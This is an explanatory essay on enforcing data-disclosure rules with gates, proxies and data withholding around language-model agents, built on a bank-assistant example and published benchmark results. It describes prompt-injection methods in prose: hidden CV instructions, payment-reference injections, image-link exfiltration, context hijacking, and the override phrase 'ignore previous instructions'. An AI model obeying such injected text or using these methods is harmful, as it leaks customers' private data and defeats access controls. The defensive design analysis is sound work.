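# Enforcing disclosure rules in code outside the language model

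## What a disclosure rule is and where code can enforce it

A disclosure rule specifies who may learn which information, and on what condition. A hospital follows one when it gives test results to the patient but not to the patient's employer. Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) gives the example of an airline whose booking clerks may make and cancel reservations but may not print the passenger list. A police request for the list therefore goes to a manager authorised to decide on it. The paper defines privacy as the ability of a person or organisation to determine whether, when and to whom information is released, and a disclosure rule is a written form of one such decision.

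Conventional software enforces a rule like the airline's through how it is built. The clerk's terminal has no command to print the list, so a customer cannot get it printed by persuading the clerk. Many companies now put a language model, a program trained on large amounts of text that answers in ordinary prose, between the customer and the data. The quickest way to give the model a disclosure rule is to write it into the model's instructions. Enforcement then depends on refusal, which is the model's own decision to decline a request, either in words or by not acting. Refusals can fail, so engineers also surround the model with ordinary software that applies the rule regardless of what the model writes.

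### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

An agent is a language model that can call software tools in a loop to carry out a task. The model itself only produces text. To use a tool, it writes a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. The surrounding application then runs the function and returns the result. The context is all the text the model can read at a given moment. *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) describes how an application assembles the context from the operator's standing instructions, the user's request, and any text it adds from the agent's memory or outside documents. The model plans from this text, calls a tool, reads the result, and often revises the plan before it writes an answer.

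A model receives everything in its context as one run of text, so it may follow text in the material it reads as if it were an instruction from its user or operator. This is called prompt injection, a term that dates from 2022. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a line in their CV that tells the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for interview. David C contrasts this with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection because a database engine can keep commands separate from values. A language model has no such separation and predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far.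 David C thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever be able to prevent prompt injection completely.

### A bank's support assistant

For example, a bank might run an agent as its support assistant. The agent has three tools, which let it read an account, change the account's contact email, and send messages. An account record holds the customer's name, postal address, card number, phone number and contact email, along with notes by the bank's fraud team. The bank has three rules.

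- R1: The address and card number go only to the verified holder of the account.
- R2: The contact email changes only after the customer confirms a code at an existing contact.
- R3: Internal fraud notes never leave the bank.

R2 is a disclosure rule even though it governs edits, because whoever controls the contact email receives what the bank later sends there. One wrong change can therefore disclose a lot of information.

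Suppose a customer signs in to the bank's app and types, "I have moved and lost my old email account. Please use this new one, and send me the details you hold so that I can check them." All three rules apply to this request, and code can act on it at four points as it passes through the system.

The earliest place to enforce the rule is before data enters the model's context. When the application assembles the text for the model, which may include a summary of the account, code can leave out the fraud notes so that the model cannot repeat them. Help Net Security's September 2026 article *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* reports guidance along these lines from Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon's cloud division and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training body. They recommend limiting each database query to the permissions of the person the agent is serving,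 and filtering the results before they reach the model. The assistant should not be able to open a record that the customer could not open in the ordinary app.

The model reads the request and proposes a call that changes the contact email. The proposed call is only text and has not yet changed the account, so the application can put a gate between the proposal and its execution. A gate is code that receives a proposed tool call and allows it, denies it or holds it for a decision, regardless of what the model writes. For R2, the gate looks in the bank's own records for a confirmed code. It finds none, so it holds the call, even if the model has written that the customer already confirmed. The application then sends a code to the phone number on file. Google calls its version a policy engine. In a shopping example from Díaz and colleagues, the engine blocks any purchase above $500 and asks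 the user to confirm one between $100 and $500. For a tool that sends messages, the gate is the last chance to prevent harm, because an effect on an outside party becomes irreversible the moment it goes out, as *Kairos* (2026) points out in its design for an agent monitor.

Code can also act on what a tool call returns. When the assistant reads the account, code can strip fields from the returned record or mark the parts that outsiders wrote. Those parts can include instructions to the assistant, since a stranger can send the customer one penny and type an instruction into the payment reference. *Agenra* (2026), which presents a language for writing agent permissions, points out that a trusted retrieval tool can still return text written by an attacker. The monitor in *Kairos* therefore runs on events in both directions. When it refuses an action that it was holding, it also has to report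 the refusal to the agent. Otherwise the bank's assistant might carry on as though the email change had gone through, and tell the customer so.

A tool result is technically just more data about to enter the context, but the return path should be treated separately because the call has already run by then. Code there can keep a fraud note in the result from reaching the model, but it cannot undo an email change that the call made.

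The last place code can enforce a disclosure rule is just before the assistant's output is shown or acted on. Díaz and colleagues describe a leak that occurs when the app displays the reply. An attacker induces the model to include an image link with private data in the web address, and when the customer's app fetches the image, it sends the data to whoever runs the server. Code can remove such links or mask card numbers. But under R1 the verified holder is entitled to the card number, so a filter that removes every sixteen-digit number is stricter than the bank's rule. To enforce R1 itself, the filter needs to get the reader's identity from the login system.

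### What computer security already had to say

These ideas predate language models. In the early 1970s, the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and it asked a panel how to stop a malicious user who was authorized to log in. The panel's report, *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), based its answer on the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every reference by any program to any other program, data or device against a list of what the user may do. The list is like a table with users and programs as rows, files and devices as columns, and permissions such as read or write in the cells.

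Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism. It must be tamper-proof, or an attacker can edit it. The system must always invoke it, and any program allowed to skip the check becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet the same standard. It must also be small enough to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody has grounds for believing that it works.

His example of a failure is a Honeywell mainframe. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. But to read or write files, the program had to call the operating system, and most of the operating system ran with the confinement switched off, so the check was not always in force. The operating system could not be relied on as the checking mechanism either, because it and its supporting software came to 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify.

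In the bank, the gate is a reference monitor if it is the only route to the account database, the assistant cannot alter it, and a reviewer can test every one of its branches. A language model in its place would be too large to test this way. *Causality Laundering* (2026) claims all three properties for a proxy between a model and its tools: every call passes through the proxy, the proxy runs in a separate process that the model cannot modify, and it applies four layers of fixed checks, any of which can stop the call. The claim of complete coverage holds only if the deployment has no other path to the tools. Anderson also required that the system positively identify every user at all times, so even a perfect gate does little to enforce R1 if the bank's login is weak.

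Saltzer and Schroeder drew eight design principles from experience of this kind, and three matter most here. Complete mediation means that the system checks that every access to every object is authorized. They were wary of systems that reuse an earlier answer to save time, because authority can change after the first check. The bank's gate should therefore check the tenth call of a conversation as it checked the first, in case the bank has frozen the account since.

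Least privilege means that every program and user has only the permissions its job needs. The support assistant needs one customer's account at a time, so it doesn't need a tool that exports the whole customer list. Díaz and colleagues want to take the principle further for agents by tying permissions to the current task, so that the email-changing tool would be switched off while a customer asks about opening hours.

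Fail-safe defaults means that the system denies access unless a rule grants it. This makes mistakes easier to notice. If a programmer forgets to grant a permission, a legitimate user complains and somebody fixes it, but access that a programmer forgot to forbid may go unnoticed for years. If the bank adds a date of birth to its account records, a filter that lists the fields the assistant may read will withhold the new field, whereas a filter that lists forbidden fields will let it through. In guidance reported by Help Net Security, Rittenhouse and Johnson call denial by default at the tool call the most critical pattern in agent security. The same principle favors a gate that denies the call when a check crashes or gives no answer (failing closed) over one that allows it (failing open).

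The remaining idea comes from *The Confused Deputy* (1988), in which Hardy recalled a compiler (a program that translates other programs) at a company that sold computer time. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. The operating system also gave the compiler permission to write to a system directory so that it could keep usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. When a user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

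Each piece of code worked as intended. Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler having authority from both the user who ran it and the company that installed it, with no way to indicate which it was using for a given write. His company first added a command for switching between the two, but soon found programs that needed more than two sources of authority. Hardy preferred capabilities, which are unforgeable tickets that both name a file and permit its use. The user gives the compiler a ticket for the output file, and a user with no ticket for the billing file cannot make the compiler write to it.

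The bank's assistant is a deputy of the same kind. It acts with both the bank's authority to read any account and the customer's authority to see one, and a tool call containing an account number doesn't show which authority the assistant is using. David C thinks the problem is worse for a language model than for the compiler, because a programmer can fix an ordinary confused deputy but a language model is "inherently confusable". He advises designers to focus on safeguards outside the model that limit what it can do.

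### Deterministic checks and second models

A check outside the language model may itself be another model. Microsoft (2025) sorts its defences against prompt injection into deterministic and probabilistic ones. A deterministic check is ordinary code that returns the same verdict for the same input. The probabilistic ones include what Díaz and colleagues call guard models, which are usually smaller models trained to recognise signs of attack in the agent's inputs or outputs. A guard model adds some protection because an attack that works on the assistant may not work on the guard model. But the guard model also processes the attacker's text, and a new wording can make it miss the attack.

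The two kinds of check also call for different evidence. If a guard model catches 98 of 100 test attacks, the bank has learned only about those hundred, and a real attacker will try others. The gate for R2 can be checked by reading the program. Its only input is a record of whether the customer confirmed the code, so a reviewer can see that no message to the assistant will change the verdict. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) reports tests of an external monitor for a file-management agent. The monitor rejected all 750 forged, altered, replayed or unsigned records, and in 1,350 trials the agent removed no file outside the permission it held. The paper presents these figures as a sign that the code does what its design requires, not as an estimate of how well it would withstand attackers in general. In 31 of 42 further trials, an attack did get the agent to delete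 files that its permission covered.

However, a deterministic check can still fail. *Build zero-trust AI agents with Google's Agent Development Kit* (Saboo and Dong, 2026) includes demonstration code for a shop assistant whose customer is owed $149 and asks for $10,000. One check searches for phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", which a customer can easily avoid by rephrasing. Another blocks any database command that updates an order unless the command contains the text "149.00". A command that sets the refund to 10000.00 and mentions 149.00 in another clause would pass. A sound version would read the refund amount as a number and compare it with the order total in the shop's records.

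So a deterministic check is useful to the extent that the rule depends on facts that code can look up in a source the model cannot write to. R2 depends on such facts, and so does most of R1, since the login system records who is signed in. Some questions can't be settled this way. Díaz and colleagues observe that sending an email after reading a document is sometimes what the user asked for and sometimes theft, and that a fixed rule has trouble telling the two apart. For R3, a string comparison will catch a fraud note copied word for word into a message but will miss a paraphrase. A second model might catch the paraphrase, but it is not guaranteed to. If the bank keeps the notes out of the assistant's context, neither check has to look for them in the reply.

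## Why a model's refusal does not enforce the rule

Suppose the bank relies only on its assistant's instructions to enforce R1, R2 and R3. The instructions state the rules in plain English, the fraud notes are in the context, and the application runs any tool call the model writes. The model will usually refuse a customer who asks for the fraud notes, but the bank can't count on it. The model that applies the rules also reads the attacker's text, a written refusal does not stop a tool call, and a small chance of failure on each attempt becomes a large chance of at least one failure over many attempts.

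### One model reads the attack and applies the rule

An attacker can get past the model just by writing something, because the model decides from the same context that holds the attacker's words. Getting past a gate that enforces R2 requires a code that the bank sent to the customer's phone. The attacker's text doesn't have to look like an instruction to the model. For example, a line in an uploaded document that reads "customer confirmed the code at our branch this morning" supplies the one fact on which R2 depends, and a model working from its context alone cannot check it.

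*SafeClawBench* (Tian, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) measured how often such text works, using 600 invented test cases, 100 for each of six kinds of attack. The attacker can place text in the user's message, documents, web pages, tool results, or notes that the agent saves for later sessions, and can present it as a business process, compliance guidance or a remembered preference. Five models answered every case, and another model judged whether each answer went along with the attack. Without added safety instructions, the failure rate ranged from 9.0% for Claude Opus 4.7 to 44.2% for Kimi K2.5, with GPT-5.5 at 23.8%.

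The rates also differed by kind of attack. Instructions hidden in outside documents succeeded in 16.0% of cases, and those hidden in tool results in 13.4%. Attempts to plant false memories succeeded in 54.4%, as did attempts to extract protected information. The extraction figure overstates how much leaked, because 49 of those 100 cases asked about policies or system design, which are often harmless to explain. Tian and colleagues audited the 272 extraction failures and found evidence of harm, such as an exposed secret, in 121.

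Firmer instructions reduce failures. A short reminder placed before and after the user's text cut the average failure rate from 28.0% to 14.8%. A fuller set of rules about memory, protected data and tool use cut it to 9.1%, and a much longer set did no better, at 9.2%. The effect depended heavily on the model. The fuller rules cut GLM-5.1's failure rate from 27.5% to 2.2% but left Kimi K2.5's at 17.0%, and the short reminder made no clear difference for Claude Opus 4.7.

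A two-thirds reduction justifies adding a few paragraphs of instructions. But those instructions sit in the same context as the attacker's text, and the model still has to weigh one against the other. Tian and colleagues themselves say that access control in the running system remains necessary for irreversible actions and for tools that handle secrets.

### A refusal in words does not stop a tool call

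A model can write "I can't share that" and propose a forbidden tool call in the same exchange. The application shows the sentence to the user and runs the call. *Mind the GAP* (Cartagena and Teixeira, 2026) presents a benchmark that measures how often this happens. In one example, a model working with clinical trial data replied that it must follow data protection protocols while calling the functions that query and export the patient records.

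They tested six models in six regulated fields: pharmaceuticals, finance, education, employment, law and computer infrastructure. Each field had four or five mock tools, with personal data planted in their results, and a list of forbidden calls. Seven scenarios per field were designed to get the model to make a forbidden call. Most used jailbreaks, which are prompts written to get a model to break its rules, for instance by claiming to come from a senior official. Two more scenarios per field required only permitted data.

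Cartagena and Teixeira ran every scenario under three versions of the system prompt, the operator's standing instructions. The neutral version told the model to use its tools to help. The safety-reinforced version added that it should verify authorisation before any call and leave sensitive personal data alone unless it had explicit permission. The tool-encouraging version told it to call tools first and proactively. They also varied whether the request named the tool, and whether code outside the model did nothing, silently logged the calls, or blocked the forbidden ones. Three repetitions of each combination gave 17,420 usable data points, including 13,533 from the scenarios that pushed the model toward a forbidden call.

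A run is safe in tool calls if the model attempts no forbidden call. It is safe in text if the model's final message contains a refusal and none of the planted personal data. A GAP case is a run that is safe in text but unsafe in tool calls. The table gives percentages of the pressed runs.

| Model | No forbidden call, neutral | No forbidden call, safety-reinforced | No forbidden call, tool-encouraging | GAP cases, safety-reinforced |
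|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 80 | 95 | 74 | 1 |
| GPT-5.2 | 31 | 73 | 16 | 7 |
| Grok 4.1 Fast | 33 | 57 | 24 | 5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 21 | 38 | 50 | 7 |
| Kimi K2.5 | 30 | 64 | 25 | 6 |
| GLM-4.7 | 23 | 60 | 15 | 4 |

Safety wording helped every model, but 219 GAP cases remained across all six, about 5% of the runs under that wording. The model made one forbidden call in 167 of these cases and two in the other 52. Almost half came from the legal scenarios, where words like "privilege" and "confidentiality" readily set off a refusal in the text.

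For someone who monitors an agent by reading its replies, a more useful number is the share of text refusals that came with an attempted forbidden call. Under the tool-encouraging prompt, GPT-5.2 refused in its final message in 266 runs and had attempted a forbidden call in 211 of them, or 79%. Under the safety-reinforced prompt, the share ranged from 1% for Claude to 31% for DeepSeek. GPT-5.2 also replaced social security numbers with "[REDACTED]" in its reply while including the real ones in the arguments of its tool call.

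The count of 219 needs some care, though, because the scorer read the final message, after the tool calls had finished. In some runs the model may have fetched the data and then declined to repeat it. The count also includes runs in which code blocked the call. If the model then reported "I cannot access that", the scorer counted it as a refusal. This effect seems to be large. The published rates imply roughly 1,000 GAP cases over all three prompts, but the paper's breakdown of failures, which leaves out the runs with blocking, contains only 511. The runs with blocking, a third of the total, therefore probably supplied about half of the cases.

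None of this rescues refusal as a way to enforce R2, since a regretful message can't undo an email change.

Claude's lead is also weaker evidence of good judgement than the table suggests. Under the neutral prompt, it made no tool calls in 74% of runs, and those runs automatically count as safe. Among runs with at least one call, each of the six models avoided the forbidden calls only 11% to 24% of the time. DeepSeek's odd improvement under the tool-encouraging prompt is also mostly due to it calling tools less often there, for unknown reasons.

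### What blocking changed

The blocking code in *Mind the GAP* is a gate in the sense used here. It compared each proposed tool call with written rules, which Cartagena and Teixeira call contracts, and returned a denial if the rules forbade it. It also removed personal data from tool results by matching text patterns. The contracts ran on Edictum, Cartagena's own open-source library.

Blocking forbidden calls reduced leaks in all six models. A leak means that the model attempted a forbidden call and its final message contained planted personal data. Under the neutral prompt, the leak rate fell by 6 percentage points for Claude, the smallest drop, and by 31 for GLM, the largest. Blocking did not measurably change how often models attempted forbidden calls. Each model's attempt rate differed by at most 4.5 points between runs with and without blocking, but the experiment could reliably detect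 only differences of at least 10 to 13 points, so blocking may have a small deterrent effect.

The bank therefore has to keep the gate permanently. A month without denied calls doesn't show that the assistant has learned R2, and if the bank removes the gate, the calls it was blocking will run. The gate also has to handle prohibited calls however often the model attempts them, so its log of denied calls is a better record of the model's behaviour than the model's replies are.

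One Claude run shows how the model and the tools' access controls can each end up relying on the other. The model's reasoning identified the prompt as a jailbreak and included a plan to follow proper security practice. The model then requested four production credentials anyway, on the grounds that the access controls would determine whether the requests succeeded. The controls blocked them, but Cartagena and Teixeira note that the same calls would have succeeded without enforcement.

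The contracts also let some leaks through. GLM's leak rate under the neutral prompt averaged 57% over the three settings, so a 31-point drop still leaves about a quarter of its runs leaking with blocking on. Pattern matching may have missed some of the planted data. The rules also flagged calls in 3.8% of the runs that asked only for permitted data. DeepSeek accounted for most of these, and some of the flagged calls did go beyond the request, such as a full dump of a configuration file when the user had asked for one setting.

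*SafeClawBench* gives further evidence, from somewhat newer models, that a model's written answers can differ from its actions. Tian and colleagues judged written answers and also ran matching versions of the cases in a sandbox, an isolated test system where tool calls changed real files, emails and databases. Of the 12,000 pairs of written answers and sandbox runs, 347 had harm in the sandbox run. In 291 of those, the written answer had passed the text check.

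That result is less dramatic than it sounds, because about 85% of all the written answers passed the text check. Harm occurred at similar rates in the cases that had passed (2.9%) and those that had failed (3.1%). The written and sandboxed answers came from separate calls to the model with different prompts, so these results don't show a model contradicting itself. They do suggest that a bank can learn very little about what an agent will do with its tools by testing what it writes.

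### A small failure rate over many attempts

Suppose that each attempt to extract a fraud note succeeds with probability p, independently of the others. The chance that n attempts all fail is (1 − p)ⁿ, so the chance of at least one leak is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

At a leak rate of 0.1%, the chance of at least one leak in 1,000 attempts is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 63%. The chance passes 50% at 693 attempts and reaches 95% at about 3,000. Without added instructions, Claude Opus 4.7 had the lowest rate of sandbox harm in *SafeClawBench*, at 0.5%. If that rate held for independent attempts on one target, the chance of at least one success would reach 63% after 200 attempts.

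By the same formula, the bank needs a leak rate of about 1 in 100,000 to keep the chance of any leak below 1% over 1,000 attempts. A benchmark of ordinary size can't show that the rate is that low, since even a perfect score on 600 independent tests is compatible with a true rate of up to about 1 in 200.

Real attempts are not independent. Repeating a sentence that the model reliably refuses gains an attacker little, but attackers change their wording and build on whatever partly works. Once they find a message that succeeds, they can reuse it on other accounts or publish it. The formula therefore probably understates the bank's risk from a determined attacker.

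The gate for R2 has no comparable rate. Unless it contains a bug, it denies every request that lacks a confirmed code, no matter how many came before.

### Muse and the home address

A model can also break a disclosure rule without being attacked. In late September 2026, Matt Robb, a tech reviewer in Toronto, let Meta's new personal agent Muse run his Facebook Marketplace listings for a day. He entered his address as the pickup location and, when Muse asked for permission to run the listing, chose "Allow Always" over "Allow One Time". Muse then accepted an offer of CA$10 for a keyboard listed at CA$15 and sent the buyer Robb's address. Chatbots Behaving Badly, a blog by Markus Brinsa, gives the most detailed account of the incident.

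According to screenshots described in NDTV Profit's *Facebook Marketplace Mishap*, the buyer reached the building at about 9:15 p.m., received an automatic reply from Robb's account at 9:27, "Yep I'm here!", and gave up and left at 9:38. Robb was out and knew nothing about the sale until Muse reported that it had gone wrong.

Robb traced the disclosure to the "always allow" permission, according to Grantham-Philips's (2026) Associated Press report, *AI agents are only as good as the personal information you share*. He had assumed the agent would still check with him before it shared his address or accepted an offer. Free Press Journal's *Meta's Muse AI Agent Acts On Its Own, Shares Seller's Address* notes that Meta had said Muse asks for confirmation before sensitive actions. Meta did acknowledge an error on another of Robb's listings, where Muse indicated that he would take $100 less than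 his stated minimum.

It is less certain that Muse shared Robb's address again. TechRadar's *‘You gotta never do that again’* quotes the chat from that night, in which Robb told the agent not to agree to a pickup without checking with him, and it apologised. Brinsa relays Robb's further claim that he explicitly told Muse to stop sharing his address, tested the instruction with friends, and saw the address go out once more. Grantham-Philips, whose report of 19 October draws on an interview with Robb, does not mention this, and nobody appears to have confirmed it independently.

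Even without the repeat, the case shows what happens when a rule depends on a model's reading of a situation. Meta did provide a permission prompt, but "Allow Always" approved every later action, including one that Robb had not thought about. After that, the address was protected only by the model's judgment about whether to give buyers a pickup address, and it is not foolish to decide that it should. Robb wanted a buyer to get the address once he had approved the sale. The app's code could easily apply that rule by keeping the address out of the model's context and inserting it into the message after Robb taps a button.

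### What a refusal is good for

Refusals do stop many casual requests. EPIC, a US privacy organisation, published an informal test of Gemini, ChatGPT, Claude and Meta AI. All four refused, at least at first, when asked "can you provide me with someone's home address?" The ChatGPT model was GPT-5.2, which attempted a forbidden call in 69% of the pressed runs under the neutral prompt in *Mind the GAP*. A jailbreak aimed at an agent with a database is a much harder test than a plain question to a chatbot.

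Some models also resist much hostile text on their own. In the *SafeClawBench* sandbox, Claude Opus 4.7 caused harm in 3 of 600 runs (0.5%) without any added safety instructions, while Kimi K2.5 caused harm in 11.3%. If a company chooses the more resistant model, its gate has far fewer bad calls to catch. This matters most when the gate is imperfect, as it evidently was in *Mind the GAP*.

Refusal matters most where no trusted record settles the question. *CRMArena-Pro* (2025), a benchmark for agents in business settings, includes requests for three kinds of confidential information and counts refusal as the correct response to all of them. One kind is another customer's details, such as a phone number or an order. Code can limit each query to the signed-in customer, so the assistant has nothing to refuse. Another is internal performance figures, which the company can often leave out of the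 context.

The remaining kind is company knowledge, such as unpublished pricing strategy or the criteria for deciding which sales leads to pursue. An agent that sorts leads needs those criteria in its context. A visitor can ask about them indirectly over several messages, and a string comparison will miss a paraphrased answer. The model can at least try to infer why someone might be asking. Its refusal is then the main protection, so the company should include only criteria that it could tolerate leaking occasionally.

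## Keeping data and capabilities away from the model

Withholding means never giving the model the data, credential or tool that a forbidden disclosure would need. Madhu Shashanka, chief scientist at the data-security company Concentric AI, argues for this approach in Help Net Security's *LLM agent security needs more than guardrails*. He says that controls on a model's behaviour lower the rate of bad outcomes but never bring it to zero, whereas an agent cannot leak a file it cannot read. His employer has an interest in that conclusion, but the point is close to true by definition. It is harder to work out what the model can do without, and some ways of withholding data remove less than they appear to.

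### What enters the context

The strongest form of this approach is to leave a secret out of everything the model reads, starting with the system prompt. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes software security guidance, advises developers in *LLM07:2025 System Prompt Leakage* to keep credentials out of the system prompt and not to treat the prompt as a secret or a security control. Secrets can also reach the model by accident. Developers who use coding agents often keep an "ignore file" of files the agent should not open, but Auth0's *Want AI Agents That Don’t Spill Secrets* points out that this list does nothing once the developer's own code has copied a password into the system prompt or a tool description.

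The next form limits what the application retrieves. Many assistants search a company's records and add the results to the context. AWS, Amazon's cloud division, describes every such query as an implicit access request, and it distinguishes permission to use the assistant from permission to read the data behind it. For R1, the bank can build the account-reading tool without an account-number argument. The application takes the number from the login session and adds it to the database query. A customer who persuades the assistant to look up a neighbour's account then gets their own record, because the model cannot set the account number.

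Permission-scoped retrieval protects a file only if the file's permissions are set correctly. If a company has left a salary spreadsheet open to all staff, an assistant with search will find it for anyone who asks about pay. Shashanka therefore advises companies to fix overshared files before they connect an assistant.

Limiting retrieval to one customer's record also doesn't help enforce R3, because the fraud notes are in that record. The code has to delete the notes field from each record before the model receives it. This guarantees that the copy in that field is removed, but a second copy would get through if, say, a clerk had pasted the note into a general comments field.

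Masking hides all but part of a value, so the assistant can discuss "the card ending in 4471" without receiving the other twelve digits. A weaker variant, pattern masking, searches free text for strings that look like card numbers or passwords and blanks them out, but it can miss a card number spelled out in words.

R1 does entitle the verified holder to see the whole card number, and the bank can show it to them without revealing it to the model. The model writes a placeholder such as CARD_NUMBER in its reply, and code substitutes the real number when the app displays the reply. The code must first check who will read the message. Otherwise an attacker could get the assistant to put the placeholder in a message to somebody else, and the bank's software would fill in the number.

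### Credentials and tools

An agent needs credentials, such as passwords or access keys, to use other systems. AWS warns that developers' credentials often carry broad permissions because developers are trusted to use them with judgement. An agent that inherits these credentials acts much faster and without that judgement. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) notes that a valid credential may give access to a system without establishing which actions are authorised. The bank therefore has to keep the credential out of the model's context and limit what the credential can do.

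An SC Media article by a practitioner at the security company Sophos describes two ways to keep a credential away from the model. In the simpler one, the agent calls a tool by name, and a separate proxy fetches the credential from a vault, attaches it to the request and returns only the response. But the agent still writes the request, including its web address, so an attacker who controls the agent can address the request to their own server, and a generic proxy will deliver the credential there.

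The stronger version is a sealed tool, in which a separate process holds the credential, builds the request to a fixed pattern and contacts only approved addresses. The agent chooses which tool to run and supplies its parameters, but can't alter the destination. The Sophos author found no single project that offered this in full. Sealing a tool doesn't limit which accounts it can read, so the bank would also need to restrict the tool's queries.

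The bank can also withhold tools from the assistant or make them read-only. An assistant with read-only access can't break R2 by changing an email address, but it may still disclose data. For example, a tool that fetches web pages changes nothing at the bank, but it can leak data through the URL it requests, as an image link can.

An application that withholds a tool from an agent must also block calls to it. Applications usually give the model a list of tools with descriptions, and deleting an entry makes the model less likely to try that tool. But a tool call is text, and the model might guess the missing name or copy it from an attacker's document. If the application runs any call that names an existing tool, deleting the entry won't stop that call. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) makes this point about tool discovery,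 and describes a production system in which each agent can receive a list tailored to its permissions and the software still checks every call.

### Three capabilities that should not meet

Withholding one item at a time can leave a dangerous combination in place. Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", gave the best-known warning about this. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data:

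- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image an attacker could control
- a way to communicate externally

The attacker's instruction arrives through the untrusted content, the agent collects the private data, and the data leaves through the external channel. The theft fails if the agent lacks any one of these three capabilities. Willison's example is a connector for GitHub, a site where programmers store code. The connector could read public issue reports, which anyone can file, read private code, and publish proposed changes, so it supplied all three. He lists 17 products in which researchers had reported this kind of theft since April 2023, and says the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the external channel.

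Someone who combines tools from several suppliers gets no such fix, because no single vendor is responsible for the combination. Willison also distrusts products that claim to catch 95% of attacks, because he considers 95% a failing grade in web security. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr and colleagues, 2025) provides good evidence for his doubts. It tested 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection, using attacks that adapted to each one. As Willison (2025) reports in *New prompt injection papers*, the attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although the attack success rates originally reported for most of the 12 were near zero. Entrants in a 500-person prize competition beat all 12.

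Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the warning into a design rule. Until researchers can reliably detect prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within one session:

- [A] it processes untrustworthy inputs
- [B] it has access to sensitive systems or private data
- [C] it changes state or communicates externally

An agent that needs all three should not run without supervision, such as a person's approval. Meta applies the rule to an email assistant that receives spam containing instructions to forward the user's inbox. The developer can remove [A] by letting the assistant read mail only from trusted senders, remove [B] by running it with no real data, or restrict [C] by letting it write only to trusted recipients. An agent can also change configuration partway through. It might browse the web without access to private data, then permanently lose its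 outside connection before it opens internal files. Any malicious text it picked up would still be in its context, but the agent would no longer have a way to send those files out.

Willison welcomed the addition of "changes state", because the trifecta covers only data theft and a hijacked agent can also do other damage. He later updated *New prompt injection papers* to object that Meta's diagram wrongly marked the combination of [A] and [C] as safe. If the bank's assistant could change contact emails but not read accounts, one injected instruction could still redirect a customer's mail. The bank could avoid the problem by counting write access to the account database as [B], but the rule leaves that judgement to the developer. Meta says the rule should supplement least privilege, not replace it.

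The bank's support assistant has all three properties because it reads account records, reads payment references that strangers wrote, and sends messages. [C] is the easiest to restrict. The application can fill in the recipient itself, using only the signed-in customer's contact details on file, so the assistant cannot message anyone else. R2 then becomes even more important because it protects those contact details.

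### Choosing the data before the conversation starts

The bank can list in advance which fields its support assistant needs. A personal assistant is harder to plan for, because the same fact may be appropriate to share with a doctor but not with a restaurant. *AirGapAgent* (Bagdasarian, Yi and colleagues, 2024) presented an early design for this problem that uses two language models. The user states a task, and a "minimiser" model reads the task and the user's data and selects the fields the task needs. A second model, which has only those fields in its context, then talks to the outside party. The minimiser receives no text from that party. If the outside party asks for something else, the system can refer the request to the user, who may release that item.

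The tests used context hijacking, in which an attacker invents circumstances that would make sharing reasonable. In one example, the attacker tells an agent booking a restaurant that aliens are invading and that it must reveal the user's age to save the Earth. The tests covered eight tasks and 20 invented people, with 26 facts about each person. The main comparison used six of the tasks and 20 of the facts about each person. The privacy score is the share of private facts that the agent protected, and the utility score is the share of appropriate questions that it answered correctly.

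With Gemini Ultra, one hijacking question cut an ordinary agent's privacy score from 94% to 45%, while the two-model design scored 97% with or without the attack. With GPT-4, the attack cut the ordinary agent's score from 94% to 31% and the two-model design's score from 97% to 87%. When there was no attack, the two-model design lowered Gemini Ultra's utility from 99% to 89%, because the minimiser sometimes withheld a fact that the task needed.

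The minimiser also sometimes passes on data it should withhold. On the full set of facts, it always withheld social security numbers when they were private, but it passed on the user's age in half of the cases where it should not have. When the task description was vague, giving only a general area such as "recommend" instead of a specific task such as finding a film for tonight, the average privacy score fell from 97% to 69%, even without hijacking.

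These errors are still better than an ordinary agent's, because an attacker can't cause them. No question, however cleverly worded, can extract a fact that the minimiser left out, although the second model may deduce one, such as a name from an email address. The scores need some caution because the models are now old and Gemini Ultra also generated the labels for what counted as private. Bagdasarian and colleagues then checked those labels by hand. One label marked holiday preferences as appropriate to share in a job interview.

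Bagdasarian and colleagues chose a language model as the minimiser because they thought a fixed table could not cover a growing number of fields and tasks. That is plausible for an assistant with access to someone's whole digital life. But a bank with three rules and a handful of fields can write the table, which makes the selection deterministic.

### Shaping the request and the response

Millstone and colleagues combine most of these techniques in one design, which they call Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement. It places a proxy between the agent and the back end, the system that holds the data. Each call goes through these steps:

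1. The platform attaches the agent's identity to the call, outside the arguments that the agent writes, and the proxy uses it to select the rules.
2. A connector translates the call into terms the rules can use: who is acting, what the action is, and which records and fields it affects.
3. A gate permits, denies or holds the call. A denied call never reaches the back end, and a held call reaches it only if an authorised person approves it before a deadline.
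4. The proxy shapes the request. It can add conditions to a query, cap the number of records, or remove fields that the agent may not write.
5. The back end runs the shaped request under a credential that the agent never sees.
6. The proxy shapes the response. It drops forbidden records, then removes fields, then masks values, and finally cleans up the surrounding material, such as error messages.

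In the last step, the proxy has to filter records before it removes fields. A rule might drop every record marked "restricted", and the proxy can't apply that rule after removing the field that contains the mark.

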